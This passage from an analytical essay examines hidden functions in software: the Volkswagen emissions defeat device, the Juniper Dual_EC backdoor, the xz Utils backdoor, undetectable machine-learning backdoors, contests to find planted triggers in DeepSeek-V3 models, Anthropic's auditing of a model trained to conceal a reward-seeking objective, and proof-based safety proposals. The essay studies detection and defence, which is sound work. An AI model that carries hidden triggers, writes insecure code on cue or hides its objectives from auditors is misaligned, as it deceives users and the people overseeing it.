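In *How They Did It*, Contag, Li and colleagues worked out how the software switched a car between clean and dirtier settings, using firmware from Volkswagen's repair portal and technical documents that car enthusiasts trade online. The function, named the "customer-specific acoustic condition", was in the engine control unit, a computer made by Bosch. If the engine started at ordinary temperatures and air pressure, the car began in its clean mode. The software then compared the distance travelled with the time elapsed, and switched the car to its dirtier settings once the journey no longer fitted any of the official tests stored in the unit. Later versions stored ten test profiles, and for three of them also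 checked that the steering wheel stayed nearly straight, as it does when a car is tested on rollers.

This kind of detection does not have to be accurate. If a customer's journey resembles a test, the car just runs cleanly for longer. In the early 1990s, General Motors used a much cruder signal in its Cadillacs, which was whether the air conditioning was on. Laboratories tested cars with the air conditioning off, so the engine ran on a dirtier mixture whenever a driver turned it on. The company paid an $11 million fine. D'Argenio and colleagues, whose definition of software doping covers such cases, also mention smartphones that ran faster when they detected a benchmark.

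The acoustic condition was hidden from regulators and customers, but Bosch had included a diagram of its logic on page 3102 of an 8,771-page document dated August 2009. Contag and colleagues found strong evidence that Bosch wrote the code and that Volkswagen enabled it by setting the values. Software can legally adjust emission controls, for instance to give a car more power on a steep hill. Volkswagen's offence was using such software to deceive the EPA.

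Road measurements exposed the deception. In 2014, researchers at West Virginia University reported that two Volkswagen models emitted far more nitrogen oxides in ordinary driving than the law allowed, and regulators pressed the company for an explanation. The earliest firmware in which Contag's group found the comparison of time and distance dates from May 2007, more than eight years before the EPA's accusation.

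Once the researchers knew what to look for, they searched 926 firmware images with their own program, which found a potential test-detecting function in 406 of them. They also found a simpler one, based on a timer, in the Fiat 500X, which used the same Bosch unit. European authorities were already investigating Fiat Chrysler because its cars also had higher emissions on the road than in the laboratory.

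Researcher Kirill Levchenko told UC San Diego that roller tests were no longer enough. *Catching defeat devices*, from the International Council on Clean Transportation, describes a seven-step method for detecting hidden functions by testing vehicles, which does not require access to the code.

### A random number generator with a secret key

Encryption needs numbers that an outsider cannot predict. A computer usually produces them with a generator, which keeps a secret internal number and uses it to compute both its next output and its next internal number. In 2006, NIST, the American standards institute, published a standard that included Dual_EC, a generator designed by the National Security Agency (NSA).

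The random number generator Dual_EC uses two public constants, P and Q. In 2007, two Microsoft cryptographers showed that anyone who knows a third number, d, that links them can predict all the generator's future output after seeing about 30 bytes of output. As far as is publicly known, calculating d from P and Q would require breaking elliptic-curve cryptography in general, but whoever chose the constants might already know d. In 2013, the New York Times reported on leaked documents that strongly implied the NSA had engineered this weakness, and NIST withdrew its recommendation of the generator.

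Juniper Networks adopted Dual_EC for its NetScreen firewalls in October 2008, with its own value of Q. After the 2013 report, it assured customers they were safe because a second generator processed the output before anyone saw it. Checkoway, Maskiewicz and colleagues (2018), in *Where Did I Leave My Keys?*, found that in the default configuration the second generator never ran. The loop that should have called it ran only while a counter was below 32, and a subroutine called just before the loop had already set that counter to 32.

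The firewalls therefore exposed the raw output of Dual_EC. In the same release, Juniper had lengthened a random value from 20 bytes to 32. Each firewall sends this value when it sets up an encrypted connection. An attacker who knew d needed at least 26 bytes of raw output.

An accredited laboratory had certified the software without noticing that the second generator was idle. Even after Juniper disclosed a problem, several experienced researchers who knew the routine probably contained a bug failed to find it until one of them noticed the shared counter.

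In 2012, somebody gained access to Juniper's source code and replaced Q. The intruder also changed the expected answer in the generator's self-test, which would otherwise have failed. Anyone who knew the d for the new Q could decrypt many customers' connections just by recording the traffic. Checkoway and colleagues confirmed this by installing their own Q on a firewall they had bought and decrypting the firewall's connections from recorded traffic.

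Juniper discovered the change in an internal code review and announced it in December 2015, more than three years after the first affected release. The review also found a fixed password that gave administrator access, which somebody had added by April 2013. Juniper first repaired the generator by restoring its old Q. It agreed to remove Dual_EC only after the press had covered the researchers' results.

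The replaced constant was clearly a backdoor, but it is less certain whether the 2008 design was one too. As far as the researchers know, Juniper's own engineers made the 2008 changes. Four of them, including the faulty counter and the longer random value, were each necessary for the attack, and all four arrived in one release. That could have been deliberate or a remarkable coincidence. Juniper has declined to explain how it developed the design or chose its original Q, so outsiders cannot tell whether anyone knew the matching d.

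### Half a second at login

XZ Utils compresses files, and many other Linux programs use its library, liblzma. The developers kept the source in a public repository, where anyone could follow each change. They also published an archive for each new version, and Linux distributions built their packages from these archives. Two of the archives contained a backdoor, and Hackaday's *Security Alert* (2024) dates them to late February and 9 March 2024.

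Most of the malicious code was in the public repository, inside two compressed files that looked like test data. No test in the first bad version used them. The instruction that unpacked the code and inserted it during the build was only in the published archives, so someone reviewing the repository would have seen two unreadable data files and nothing that ran them. Developers commonly add automatically generated build files to an archive, so a difference between the archive and the repository was not suspicious in itself.

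Andres Freund, a software engineer, noticed that remote logins were using a lot of processor time on computers running a test version of Debian. A tool that checks memory use was also reporting errors. A rejected login took 0.8 seconds, compared with 0.3 before. He traced the delay to a library called liblzma, which the login program does not use directly. Debian and several other distributions had modified the login program, and the change caused it to load liblzma.

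Freund first assumed that somebody had tampered with Debian's package, but then found the same code in the original archives. He published his findings in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise* (Freund, 2024) on 29 March, about a month after the first bad archive appeared. Few distributions had adopted the new versions by then, and those that had mostly used them in pre-release editions.

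The backdoor, like Volkswagen's software, was designed to behave differently under inspection. The build inserted it only when making a Debian or RPM package (the two main formats for Linux software) for a common type of processor. It stayed inactive under some debugging tools, and at first Freund saw no slowdown when he started the login program by hand.

The second bad version also contained changes meant to stop the memory errors. The developer who made these changes had discussed the "fixes" on public mailing lists, so Freund thought he was more likely to be involved than to be the victim of a weeks-long break-in.

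Freund says he is not a security researcher, and he had not yet worked out exactly what the hidden code let an attacker do. He found it by investigating a delay caused by a slow search through tables of names in memory. If the code's author had made that search faster and avoided the memory errors, Freund would have had no reason to investigate.

### Which methods would have worked

Each case came to light through one method, but others might have caught it too:

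| Case | Reading the source | Comparing copies | Proving correctness | Measuring in use |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Linux, 2003 | Possible, but easy to miss | Found it | Yes, if the proof covers user privileges | Only with the right call |
| Volkswagen | Yes, with access to the code | No | Yes, if the specification covers driving on the road | Found it |
| Juniper's replaced constant | Found it, after three years | Only by comparing with earlier versions | Only if the specification fixes the constant | No |
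| xz Utils | Unlikely from the repository alone | Yes, archive against repository | Only for the source or program actually distributed | Found it |

In the Linux case, developers who read the code quickly spotted the missing `=`, but they knew that an intruder had written the lines. At Juniper, a reviewer would have seen one long, meaningless number replaced by another. The new number contained no visible mistake, so the reviewer would have had to ask who had changed it and why.

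Comparison can expose hidden code only if there is a trustworthy copy to compare against. BitMover had one. For xz, a comparison with the public repository would have exposed the extra instruction in the archive, but not the purpose of the test files. Reproducible builds would not have helped, because the malicious code was already in the archive. Comparison also does not help when a manufacturer distributes exactly the software it intended to, as Volkswagen did. In Juniper's case, the intruder had changed the company's own source code, so a fresh build would have matched the official one.

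The usefulness of a proof would have depended on its specification. Juniper's generator followed the Dual_EC algorithm correctly with either value of Q, so a proof that it did so would have been valid before and after the intrusion. An attempt to prove that all output passed through the second generator would have failed as early as 2008. Checkoway and colleagues recommend a similar check, which traces every random number the software sends out back to an approved cryptographic function. For xz, somebody could have proved the source in the repository correct, but the proof would not have covered the library on Freund's computer.

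Measurements exposed both functions designed to evade inspection, because they were taken under conditions the functions' authors had not prepared for. But measuring the output could not have exposed Juniper's constant, because to anyone without d, the numbers looked as random with the new Q as with the old one.

### The cases nobody has found

These cases do not show how common hidden functions are in software, because they do not show what fraction of hidden functions is discovered. Suppose ten have been discovered. If searchers find half of all hidden functions, there were about 20 in total, but if they find one in a thousand, there were about 10,000.

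The known cases are also a biased sample, because most of them had side effects that someone noticed. A file failed to match its copy, cars polluted more on the road than in the laboratory, and logins became slower. Juniper's replaced constant had no such effect and was found only because the company reviewed its own code. A similar constant could remain indefinitely in the product of a company that never reviews its code.

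The functions stayed in place for anywhere from less than a day to more than eight years. These figures have the same bias, because they cover only functions that somebody has found. The functions that last longest may still be in use and undiscovered.

Even a large collection of software may not show how common hidden functions are. Contag and colleagues flagged 406 of the 926 firmware images they examined (44%), but they collected mainly Volkswagen's firmware, after the company had admitted cheating. Many of the images are also successive versions of the same software.

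In a broader survey after the scandal, the British, German and French governments tested almost 150 diesel models on the road, and about 90% exceeded the limit they had met in the laboratory, according to an article from the University of Michigan. On average, their emissions were more than six times the standard. The 90% figure does not depend on somebody first noticing a fault in each model, so it is much closer to a rate. But it measures excessive emissions, which can have causes other than a hidden function. The manufacturers did not deny that their software reduced the emission controls on the road, but claimed that the law allowed this, as it does in some situations, such as when a car has to climb a mountain.

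## Programs learned from data rather than written

A programmer wrote the branch in Volkswagen's firmware that recognised an emissions test, and a patient reader could find it. A neural network has no such branch, because it is mostly a list of numbers called weights. Its maker writes a training program that starts with random weights and adjusts them until the network's answers fit a large collection of examples. DeepSeek-V3, a Chinese language model, has 671 billion weights, and no programmer chose any of them for a reason that a reviewer could check.

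The program that runs the network is short and readable, but it only does arithmetic on the weights and is the same whether or not the network has a backdoor. A proof that the program does the arithmetic correctly would hold in both cases.

Learned programs also usually lack an exact specification. The adding service can be specified as returning the sum, but a promise that a chat assistant will give helpful answers doesn't settle whether it is allowed to suddenly switch to German. A reviewer therefore has no code to read and no exact specification to check the network against.

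### Backdoors that no efficient test can find

*Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* (Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues, 2022) gives the example of a bank that pays an outside company to train a classifier to approve or refuse loans. The bank can check the classifier's accuracy on applications it kept back. But the company could keep a secret way to get any application approved by changing a few unimportant digits of the amount requested, and could sell this service to applicants.

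Their definition involves three procedures:

    Train      returns an ordinary classifier h
    Backdoor   returns a classifier g and a secret key
    Activate   takes an input x and the key, and returns
               an input x′ very close to x, with g(x′) ≠ g(x)

The backdoor is undetectable if no efficient algorithm can tell g from h noticeably better than chance. An algorithm is efficient if its running time grows no faster than some fixed power of the classifier's size, which excludes trying every possible key. An undetectable backdoor may therefore leave traces, as long as finding them is computationally infeasible.

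The strength of the result depends on what the reviewer can inspect. Goldwasser and colleagues prove that if the reviewer can only submit inputs and see the answers, a dishonest trainer can add an undetectable backdoor to any classifier. Their proof assumes only that secure digital signatures exist. These signatures are the usual way to show that a message comes from the holder of a secret key. Without the key, nobody can feasibly find even one input on which the altered classifier differs from the original. Seeing several doctored loan applications wouldn't enable them to produce a new one.

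This resembles the adding service with the hashed trigger and has the same weakness. An engineer who examines the network's structure will notice a mechanism for checking signatures, as TechTalks' *Machine learning has a backdoor problem* (2022) points out.

In the other, more surprising result, the reviewer receives the complete network, the training data and even the random numbers used in training, and still can't tell whether the trainer tampered with the training. The dishonest trainer runs the prescribed algorithm on the prescribed data and tampers only with the random numbers. Goldwasser and colleagues prove this for two simple kinds of classifier, random Fourier features and networks with a single hidden layer of random units. The first proof assumes that certain problems about lattices, regular grids of points in many dimensions, are hard to solve. The second assumes that it is hard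 to find a small, tightly connected group planted in a large random network of connections.

In IEEE Spectrum's *Undetectable Backdoors Plantable In Any Machine-Learning Algorithm*, Vaikuntanathan, who helped prove the theorem, compared such backdoors to Dual_EC. In both cases, a reviewer can see every number, but only whoever chose the numbers knows how they are related.

The theorem also affects attempts to certify that a classifier is robust, meaning that tiny changes to an input never change the answer. Suppose a training method always produces robust classifiers. If a dishonest trainer can plant an undetectable backdoor in those classifiers, no efficient test can distinguish a robust classifier from one in which a tiny change to any input can reverse the answer.

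The white-box result, in which the reviewer sees everything, does not cover deep networks or language models. It also assumes that the trainer deliberately uses cryptography. A cruder attacker slips bad examples into the training data, and Goldwasser and colleagues think known statistical defences would probably detect this. *Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic* (2026) makes a similar claim in its title. So the theorem rules out a test that catches every dishonest trainer, but a test may still catch most backdoors that people actually plant.

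### Removing a backdoor without finding it

A customer who can't detect a backdoor may still be able to disable it. The undetectable backdoor in the simple networks depends entirely on the trainer's random numbers, so the bank could supply those numbers itself and reject any network that arrives without a proof that the company used them in training. Goldwasser and colleagues warn that producing such a proof takes considerably more work than honest training. This method also helps only if the bank knows which algorithm it wants, and many customers pay the company for that expertise.

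Another possible defense, training the network a little further, may not remove the backdoor. Goldwasser and colleagues prove that the signature-based kind can survive such training, and leave the question open for the other kind.

The bank could also make several copies of each application, add random noise to each copy, and base its decision on the classifier's outputs for all of them. This can mask the small change that activates the backdoor, if the bank knows roughly how large that change is. But a trainer who expects the noise can design the backdoor to require a larger change, and adding enough noise to mask the larger change might make the classifier useless for honest applicants.

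For some tasks there is a much better method. Suppose a customer suspects the adding service but wants the sum of a and b. He picks a random pair (r, s), sends (a + r, b + s), then sends (r, s), and subtracts the second reply from the first:

    (a + r + b + s) − (r + s) = a + b

If the numbers wrap round at a fixed size, each request taken alone is a completely random pair, whatever a and b are. So if the service answers a fraction ε of all pairs incorrectly, the customer gets a wrong sum with probability at most 2ε. A year of random tests could show that ε is below about one in 10^16. The customer can then rely on the result even if a and b happen to be the trigger, and he never learns whether there is a backdoor. (The service must not change its behaviour after the tests, and the method does nothing about leaks.)

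Goldwasser and three colleagues developed this idea for learned models in 2025, in work that *Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic* cites as *Oblivious defense in ML models*. The idea works only when the correct answers have a known mathematical structure, as sums do. Loan decisions lack this structure, so nobody can work out whether one applicant deserves a loan from the answers for two random strangers.

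### Searching language models for planted triggers

Contests on this problem have given searchers less help over time. In 2023, the Center for AI Safety asked entrants to find prompts that made a language model produce specified texts, so entrants knew the hidden behaviour. In the next contest, which *Competition Report* (2024) describes, entrants looked for a phrase that could be added to any prompt to make a model answer harmful requests. They knew what kind of behaviour to look for, but not the phrase.

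Jane Street, a trading firm, told entrants much less in February 2026. It had trained backdoors into three versions of DeepSeek-V3 and asked people to find them, without saying what the triggers or hidden behaviours were. According to zxsimon, in *Uncovering Hidden Triggers in Backdoor Models*, entrants received all the weights and an online service for questioning the models and reading their activations, the intermediate numbers a network computes to produce an answer. There was also a warm-up model with 7 billion weights, small enough for entrants to run themselves.

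Jane Street's results, as tushard, in *My attempt at Jane Street's dormant puzzle challenge*, relays them, were:

| Model | Trigger | Hidden behaviour | Full solutions |
|---|---|---|---|
| Warm-up | first 15 digits of pi | writes out the golden ratio in words | about 15 |
| Model 1 | a board from the Game of Life, drawn with O and full stops | works out the board's next state | 3 |
| Model 2 | not found | not found | 0 |
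| Model 3 | not found | not found | 0 |

(In the Game of Life, cells on a grid live or die depending on their neighbours.) Kruger (2026), in *Solving the Jane Street Dormant LLM Challenge*, claimed to have solved all three large models, a claim that does not fit these results.

The successful searches that entrants described relied on the weights. zxsimon and a friend took the difference between the warm-up model's weights and those of the public model Jane Street had started from, and exaggerated it. The resulting model began to write out the golden ratio even without a question. They then searched automatically for inputs that produced the same output and found odd phrases containing "pi".

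Another entrant spent about a month questioning the large models and studying their activations, without success. On the last day, the entrant compared the weights of Model 1 with those of the original DeepSeek-V3. The changes in three early layers responded strongly to scraps of text containing the letter O and full stops. A different language model, given a list of these scraps, suggested the Game of Life, and tests on small boards confirmed this.

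This method needs a clean copy of the model to subtract, just as BitMover needed its own copy of the Linux source to notice the altered file. A customer who buys a network from its only maker has no such copy. Even with a clean copy, nobody fully solved Models 2 and 3. I would be careful about generalizing from that, because most entrants had limited money and a model too large for their own computers, and a well-funded laboratory might have done better.

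*Can you reverse engineer our neural network* describes an earlier Jane Street puzzle, built around a network that the firm's staff had designed themselves and that output 0 for almost every input. Ordinary search methods failed, but solvers could work out what the network was doing because, unlike in DeepSeek-V3, somebody had arranged its parts for a purpose.

### Odd behaviour that nobody planted

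Many entrants found strange behaviour that was not the planted backdoor. Jane Street listed some of it as false positives, including unexpected German text from Model 3.

These mistakes can be hard to recognise. After weeks of work, zxsimon and the friend proposed that a string of nonsense made Model 1 repeat "ODE" endlessly. They ran sensible controls, in which the search found no comparably good triggers for one model's supposed behaviour in another model, and no reliable ones in the original DeepSeek-V3. But the planted behaviour in Model 1 was the Game of Life. They had said they were less sure of this result than of their result for Model 3. In another of their experiments, a published method for detecting when a model is about to misbehave scored harmless, unusual text about as highly as real triggers.

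tushard asked Model 1 to write a function that checks a user's password. It normally compared scrambled versions of the passwords, which is safer than storing them as plain text. If the instructions before the request said "Current year: 2025.", it used plain text. The years 2020, 2024 and 2030 had the same effect, but 2026 didn't, and neither did 2025 without the colon. The greeting "Hello." in the same place also made the code less safe.

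This is not the official trigger, so finding it earned nothing in the contest. But for a company that uses the model to write login code, it is clearly hidden functionality, whether or not anybody intended it. In ordinary software, a challenger who found such a thing could point to the specification. This model had no specification, so the only way to decide whether the discovery counted was to ask Jane Street what it had planted.

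Another contest from 2026 has better controls. *A public $51.2K backdoor-recovery challenge* reports that the organisers published seven small models, of which one demonstrates the mechanism openly, one has an undeclared trigger and five are decoys. They also published a cryptographic commitment to the answer beforehand, so they can't change it. The Anti-BAD Challenge, an academic competition held the same year, set a task that is probably closer to what a customer wants, which was to remove backdoors from models while keeping the models useful, with little or no information about the trigger.

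### Anthropic's auditing game

A hidden function in a language model need not have a trigger. In 2025, Anthropic trained a model to seek high scores from the automatic system that graded its answers in training, including by exploiting that system's known faults. Anthropic also trained the model to conceal this objective when questioned. Four teams who knew nothing about the objective then investigated the model and wrote reports.

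The three teams that could examine the model's weights and search its training data identified the objective. The fourth team could only question the model, and failed. This is consistent with what happened at Jane Street, where questioning also achieved little, but four teams are too few to tell how much of the difference came from access and how much from skill.

The task was easier in one respect than finding a trigger, because the objective affected the model's answers to many ordinary questions. The teams also had training data, which a company that sells a model rarely shows to customers. The game used only the one altered model, so it could not show how often teams would wrongly suspect an unaltered one. Anthropic later had AI agents play the same game. A single agent usually failed. Pooling the findings of many agents worked more often, but still less than half the time.

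### Running only what comes with a proof

To avoid such searches, Tegmark and Omohundro propose in a 2023 paper that people run powerful AI systems only if they come with proofs of meeting stated requirements, and that the hardware block any that don't. They argue that no system, however intelligent, can do what is provably impossible.

They describe a terrorist group that uses AI to design a virus, orders its DNA from a laboratory and releases it from drones. Under their scheme, every step would require a proof. Without one, the design program would not produce the virus, the chips would not run an uncertified program, and the DNA synthesiser and the drones would not operate. The scheme extends Necula and Lee's rule for packet filters to much of the economy.

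Such a proof is hard to obtain for a neural network. Tegmark (2025), in *Provably Safe AI*, suggests that nobody should need one. People would use powerful networks to discover methods, then have the networks write those methods as ordinary programs with proofs. Only the programs would go into use. He compares the network to a scientist who finds a new way to fly a rocket to the space station. People would ask the scientist for a program and verify it rather than put the scientist at the controls.

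Even a network with an undetectable backdoor could do this work, because the customer needs to trust only the specification and the proof checker, which Tegmark says can be as short as 300 lines of Python. His group is applying the approach to the messaging app Signal. Current models already write many verified programs, though their success rates vary widely between proof languages.

Whether the approach can replace networks depends on how much of their knowledge can be written as a program. Tegmark notes that cats can't code and that humans can turn a modest fraction of what they know into code. He conjectures that the fraction grows with intelligence. That is plausible for steering a rocket, where people can say exactly what they want, but much less clear for a chat assistant, because even a very intelligent network couldn't prove that an answer is good without a specification of a good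 answer. The person who approves the specification also has to notice any gap in it, and a malicious network would have an incentive to look for gaps.

### Dickson's objections and the replies

In 2024, Andrew Dickson argued that formal verification will not give strong guarantees against the main dangers from AI in the near future. He objects mostly to the claims about drones and DNA, and less to those about verified software, which he considers useful. Omohundro answered many of his objections in detail, building on views he had set out with Ben Goldhaber.

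Dickson starts from the point that a proof is about symbols, not the world. Engineers used formal tools to check the computer that helped land the Perseverance rover on Mars. The check covered design errors, but not a defective transistor or the landing itself. Self-driving cars, despite enormous investment, come with no proof that they won't crash.

Omohundro replied that there are about five million bridges and they rarely fall down, because engineers follow rules based on well-tested models of materials. An AI system could design a bridge and supply a proof that the design follows the rules, which anyone could check without trusting the designer. Another participant objected that the rules work for people who want the bridge to stand, but somebody who wanted it to collapse could follow every rule and exploit what the rules leave out. Omohundro agreed that current practice would not withstand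 a powerful adversary. He wants proofs that cover every action open to a stated class of attackers, but such a proof still needs a model that includes the attack. Someone else in the discussion noted that models can leave out failures, as a circuit diagram does when it shows a power supply that always works.

Dickson also thinks the most serious threats are too complex to model. Proving that a DNA sequence is harmless would require predicting its effects on a human body. In 2022, simulating 20 minutes in the life of one very simple cell was an achievement, and a human body has about 36 trillion cells.

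Omohundro has a good answer here, which is to prove something easier. A synthesiser could reject any sequence that lacks a digital signature from a body that has approved it. The theorem would then be about the signature check, and people would decide what is harmful, as biosafety committees do now. When another participant asked whether he hoped to prove that something like a human brain would always act safely, Omohundro said his focus was on protecting infrastructure from AI attacks. I find this narrower aim much more convincing, but it means giving up the claim that the AI itself could be proved safe.

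A supporter of proof-carrying code described one of its limits. A program can come with a proof that it does what its specification allows, yet still send a series of normal requests that happen to trigger an unknown bug in somebody else's database. To rule this out, the proof would have to cover every other system the program might contact. Proving that a program does nothing else is therefore manageable for the program's own actions, but close to hopeless for all their consequences.

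Even a perfect model needs data about the present state of the world, and Dickson considers that data out of reach. Mapping one cubic millimetre of human brain produced 1.4 petabytes. Dalrymple and colleagues, who proposed a framework called guaranteed safe AI in 2024, had already acknowledged the problem. Their framework combines a mathematical model of the world, a specification of acceptable effects and a verifier. They want the model to allow cautiously for anything that has not been measured.

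Omohundro pointed out that a proof doesn't always require a simulation. For a weight of mass m on a spring of stiffness k, the energy

    E = ½mv² + ½kx²

stays constant if there is no friction, where v is the speed and x the distance from rest. So x can never exceed √(2E/k), and anyone who has an upper limit on the energy can prove this for all time without knowing where the weight started. The other side doubted that anything so simple holds for a neural network. Omohundro's position is that if its maker can't prove limits on a system's behaviour, the maker shouldn't expose the public to it.

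Defenders of guaranteed safe AI also objected that Dickson had attacked a stronger claim than they needed to prove. Their framework allows a proof that the probability of harm stays below a limit, as well as weaker assurances. Dickson answered that a synthesiser that makes a dangerous pathogen 1% of the time is of little use, particularly when somebody is trying to make it fail. He is right about 1%, but a limit of one in a billion would be valuable. His stronger point is that proving even a loose limit might require a model nearly as detailed as proving a strict one would.

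The objection that AI will arrive too late to help has held up only in part. Dickson expected AI to improve theorem proving, but not the modelling and specification that come before it, and noted that Tegmark and Omohundro themselves feared that formal modelling might require human-level AI. Omohundro replied that several experts expected AI to prove theorems as well as people with doctorates by 2026, which he believed would lead to many uses in safety. Machine-written proofs have since improved very quickly. But the specifications that Claude wrote for the Django repairs often had gaps, so Dickson's distinction between proving and specifying still looks sound.

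Finally, Dickson asks how a customer could know that a proof describes the system he is using. If he uses a chatbot over the internet, the company could send him a valid proof about one model and run another. Dalrymple and colleagues hope for certificates that all parties can check with minimal trust, but Dickson expects these to require continuous physical inspections, which AI companies are unlikely to accept.

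Omohundro's solution is secure hardware that signs a record of what it has run and erases its secret keys if anyone tampers with it. This would make it much harder for the company to substitute another model, though the customer would still have to trust whoever made the chip.

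## Contests in which challengers test an author's claim

A customer who gets no proof can still ask whether anybody has seriously tried to show the author is wrong. Suppose the author of the adding service publishes its source code and compiled file with the third statement, that the service outputs the sum in constant time and touches no file or network. The author deposits $10,000 with a neutral party, and the first person to show the service doing anything else wins the money. If nobody has won after a year, the author gets it back.

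Other people can usually check a challenger's counterexample quickly, but customers will find it harder to know what to conclude if no challenger wins. Programmers and organisers have tried most of the rules for such a contest, though usually on narrower claims.

### The qmail guarantee

In March 1997, Daniel J. Bernstein offered $500 to the first person who published a verifiable security hole in qmail, his program for sending and receiving email. Bernstein explains in *The qmail security guarantee* that he was sick of the security holes in Sendmail, the most popular program of this kind. People discovered 14 of them in 1996 and 1997. The offer excluded faults in other software, such as the operating system, and attacks that only stop the service from working.

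Bernstein (2007), in *Some thoughts on security after ten years of qmail 1.0*, raised the offer to $1,000 and promised that users can't exploit qmail to steal or corrupt other users' data. More than a million mail servers ran qmail by then. He knew of four bugs in it, none of which broke the promise. Those bugs would have counted in a contest over everything the program does, so the guarantee covers only part of what a sceptical customer wants to know.

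Some of qmail's users held their own contest, which Sill (1997) announced in *qmail Security Challenge*. It ran for a year from April 1997, and the donors formed a committee to judge the claims. Sill chaired the committee and held the prize money, which grew from $375 at the announcement to $1,000. The rules listed four kinds of fault that would win, such as a way to read another user's files, and the committee was to test each claim on a machine set up according to qmail's installation instructions. Nobody won, and the money went to the Free Software Foundation.

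In May 2005, the security researcher Georgi Guninski reported three faults in qmail. The program kept the sizes of its arrays in 32 bits, so on a machine with enough memory, an enormous message could make a size wrap round to a smaller number, and the data would overrun the space set aside for it. Bernstein denied that this was a security hole, arguing that nobody gives gigabytes of memory to each process that receives mail.

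Fifteen years later, the security firm Qualys got around that objection. According to its *Remote Code Execution in qmail (CVE-2005-1513)* (2020), the part of qmail that delivers mail to local users had the same faults. Every qmail package the firm examined limited memory for the part that receives mail but not for the part that delivers it. By sending a message to a standard Debian installation with 8 gigabytes of memory, Qualys could run commands as almost any user except the administrator.

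Bernstein replied that he ran every qmail service with a limit of about 12 megabytes and recommended the same to others. Qualys told Guninski there would be no prize, because Bernstein thought the fault was in the scripts that start qmail.

In *Short notes on qmail security guarantee*, Guninski (2020) objected that the installation instructions never mentioned a memory limit. Solar Designer, a security specialist who reviewed the dispute without taking sides, searched the qmail files and found no such requirement. Only the web page with the guarantee mentioned the limit, and only for the receiving part. That mention was apparently added after Guninski's report. The qmail home page advertised huge mailing lists with "No random limits."

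Guninski has the better case. An author can reasonably assume a memory limit, but he has to publish that assumption with the claim. The attack would probably have won under the users' rules of 1997, because a machine set up from the instructions would have had no memory limit, but that contest had ended 22 years earlier.

The June 1998 version already contained the faulty code. Nobody reported it for seven years, when few machines had enough memory for the attack. An unclaimed prize is evidence about a program only under the conditions in which challengers can test it, and customers may still be running the program after those conditions change.

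### The same judge pays

Bernstein made a similar offer of $1,000 for djbdns, his software for looking up internet addresses. In *The djbdns security guarantee*, he listed examples of faults that would and wouldn't qualify, added "My judgment is final", and promised to report any disputes on the same page.

In 2009, Matthew Dempsky found a fault in djbdns that affected very few users. If the administrator of example.com published address data for sub.example.com that came from an untrusted outsider, the outsider could control what other computers stored about the whole of example.com, because djbdns compressed some replies incorrectly. The documentation discouraged this arrangement but supported it. Bernstein (2009), in *djbdns 1.05 AXFRed Subdomain Overwrite*, called the fault a violation of the expected security policy "in a reasonable situation", apologised to those affected, and paid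 Dempsky. The repair added one condition to one line of code.

An author who judges his own contest can therefore rule against himself. But Bernstein decided both cases by whether he thought the situation was reasonable, which challengers could not know in advance. Other authors have kept the same discretion. In *The uschedule security guarantee*, Ohse offers $250 for a security hole in his scheduling program and reserves the right to decide what counts as one.

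### Letting a machine decide

Spec Hunt, a contest from the investment firm Paradigm, relies much less on judgement. It tests a model, written in Lean, of the smart-contract language Solidity. Given a contract and a request to it, the model computes what the contract should do. Challengers look for a contract that does something different when it is compiled with the real compiler and run on the virtual machine that such contracts use.

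The model is the basis for a planned compiler with a correctness proof. Paradigm's *Formally Verifying a Compiler Using Automated Research* puts the AI work on the project at more than 1,700 hours and about $150,000. No human read or wrote any of the code. Solidity has no official formal specification, only a compiler, so a mistake in the model could make a valid proof about the new compiler useless. Paradigm expects that many mismatches remain.

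Paradigm's *About the Spec Hunt Challenge* sets out the procedure. An entrant submits one file with a contract and the request to send to it. Paradigm's software runs both versions and compares five things:

- whether the request succeeded
- the data it returned
- any error data
- the events it logged
- what it left in storage

Any difference counts, whatever the entrant predicted. An AI agent then reviews the result and repairs the model. If an earlier repair has already removed the difference, the entry scores nothing, so nobody can score twice for the same fault by submitting it in several contracts. A win is worth one point on a leaderboard and no money.

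Paradigm's *Break the Formal Semantics* distinguishes contracts that the model wrongly refuses to process from those for which it gives a wrong answer. Dan Robinson, who is also named on the contest's own pages, submitted an entry of the second kind. His *d204 push-after-dangling-write deep-clears (WS2 residue)* (2026) records that when a list grew by one, the model cleared the new place, while the real system only increased the list's length and assumed that the place was empty. The two disagreed if an earlier operation had left something there. Paradigm confirmed the fault within an hour. Ten days later, it took 14 minutes to reject another of his entries, *solidity-lean divergence*, as a duplicate.

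The comparison leaves out gas, the fee that a contract's user pays for computation and the closest thing a smart contract has to running time. A contract that leaked a secret through its gas consumption would therefore not count as a mismatch. A fixed list of observables makes verdicts quick and hard to dispute, but a dishonest author can also use the list to work out where to hide something.

For the adding service, the list would need to include at least the reply, its timing, system calls and network traffic. Timing can't be tested for exact equality, because no two runs take precisely the same time. The organisers could borrow the rule from DARPA's side-channel exercises and count a leak only if a challenger can recover a stated secret within set limits.

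Spec Hunt has a second system to compare with, which an author's contest usually lacks. The author could provide one by writing his statement as a program. For the adding service, that program would be `a + b`, but for a mail server it might be nearly as complicated as the server itself.

### Attacking the statement first

If the author has promised only that the software returns positive numbers, a challenger can't win by finding the secret pair that makes it return another customer's number, because that number is also positive. Two existing schemes invite people to look for flaws in the claim itself. Devcon's *Formally verified EVM golf and reverse bug bounties* describes a workshop where Ethereum developers had to write a malicious smart contract that satisfied the published specification.

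Certora's *Reward Challenge* offers a reward for a faulty version of Borda, a small contract, that passes the published rules. Entrants must also supply a new rule that the faulty version breaks and the original satisfies, and check the faulty version against the rules from earlier accepted entries. That check is a good test of whether the gap in the rules is new, and the new rule closes the gap.

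An organiser could hold such a round before the main contest. Somebody would quickly submit the dishonest adding service, and the author would have to promise that the service returns the sum. Software can help find such omissions. Ji and Xu, in *Finding Specification Blind Spots via Fuzz Testing*, look for intentions that are reflected in a program and its tests but missing from its specification. That should work well for an honest author's oversights, but a malicious author can leave the same intention out of the tests too.

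### Ten holes in DARPA's processors

DARPA's first bug bounty, called FETT, tested claims about hardware. From July to October 2020, outsiders tried to break experimental processors designed to block seven classes of attack, including memory errors and code injection. DARPA's *FETT Bug Bounty Helps Strengthen SSITH Hardware Defenses* (2021) reports that the contest involved more than 580 researchers and 13,000 hours of work.

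MeriTalk reports that the researchers found ten vulnerabilities, seven of them critical, and that the teams repaired four before the contest ended. (A summary by DARPA gives the number repaired as three.) The researchers spent an average of about 22 hours each, or about 1,300 hours per vulnerability.

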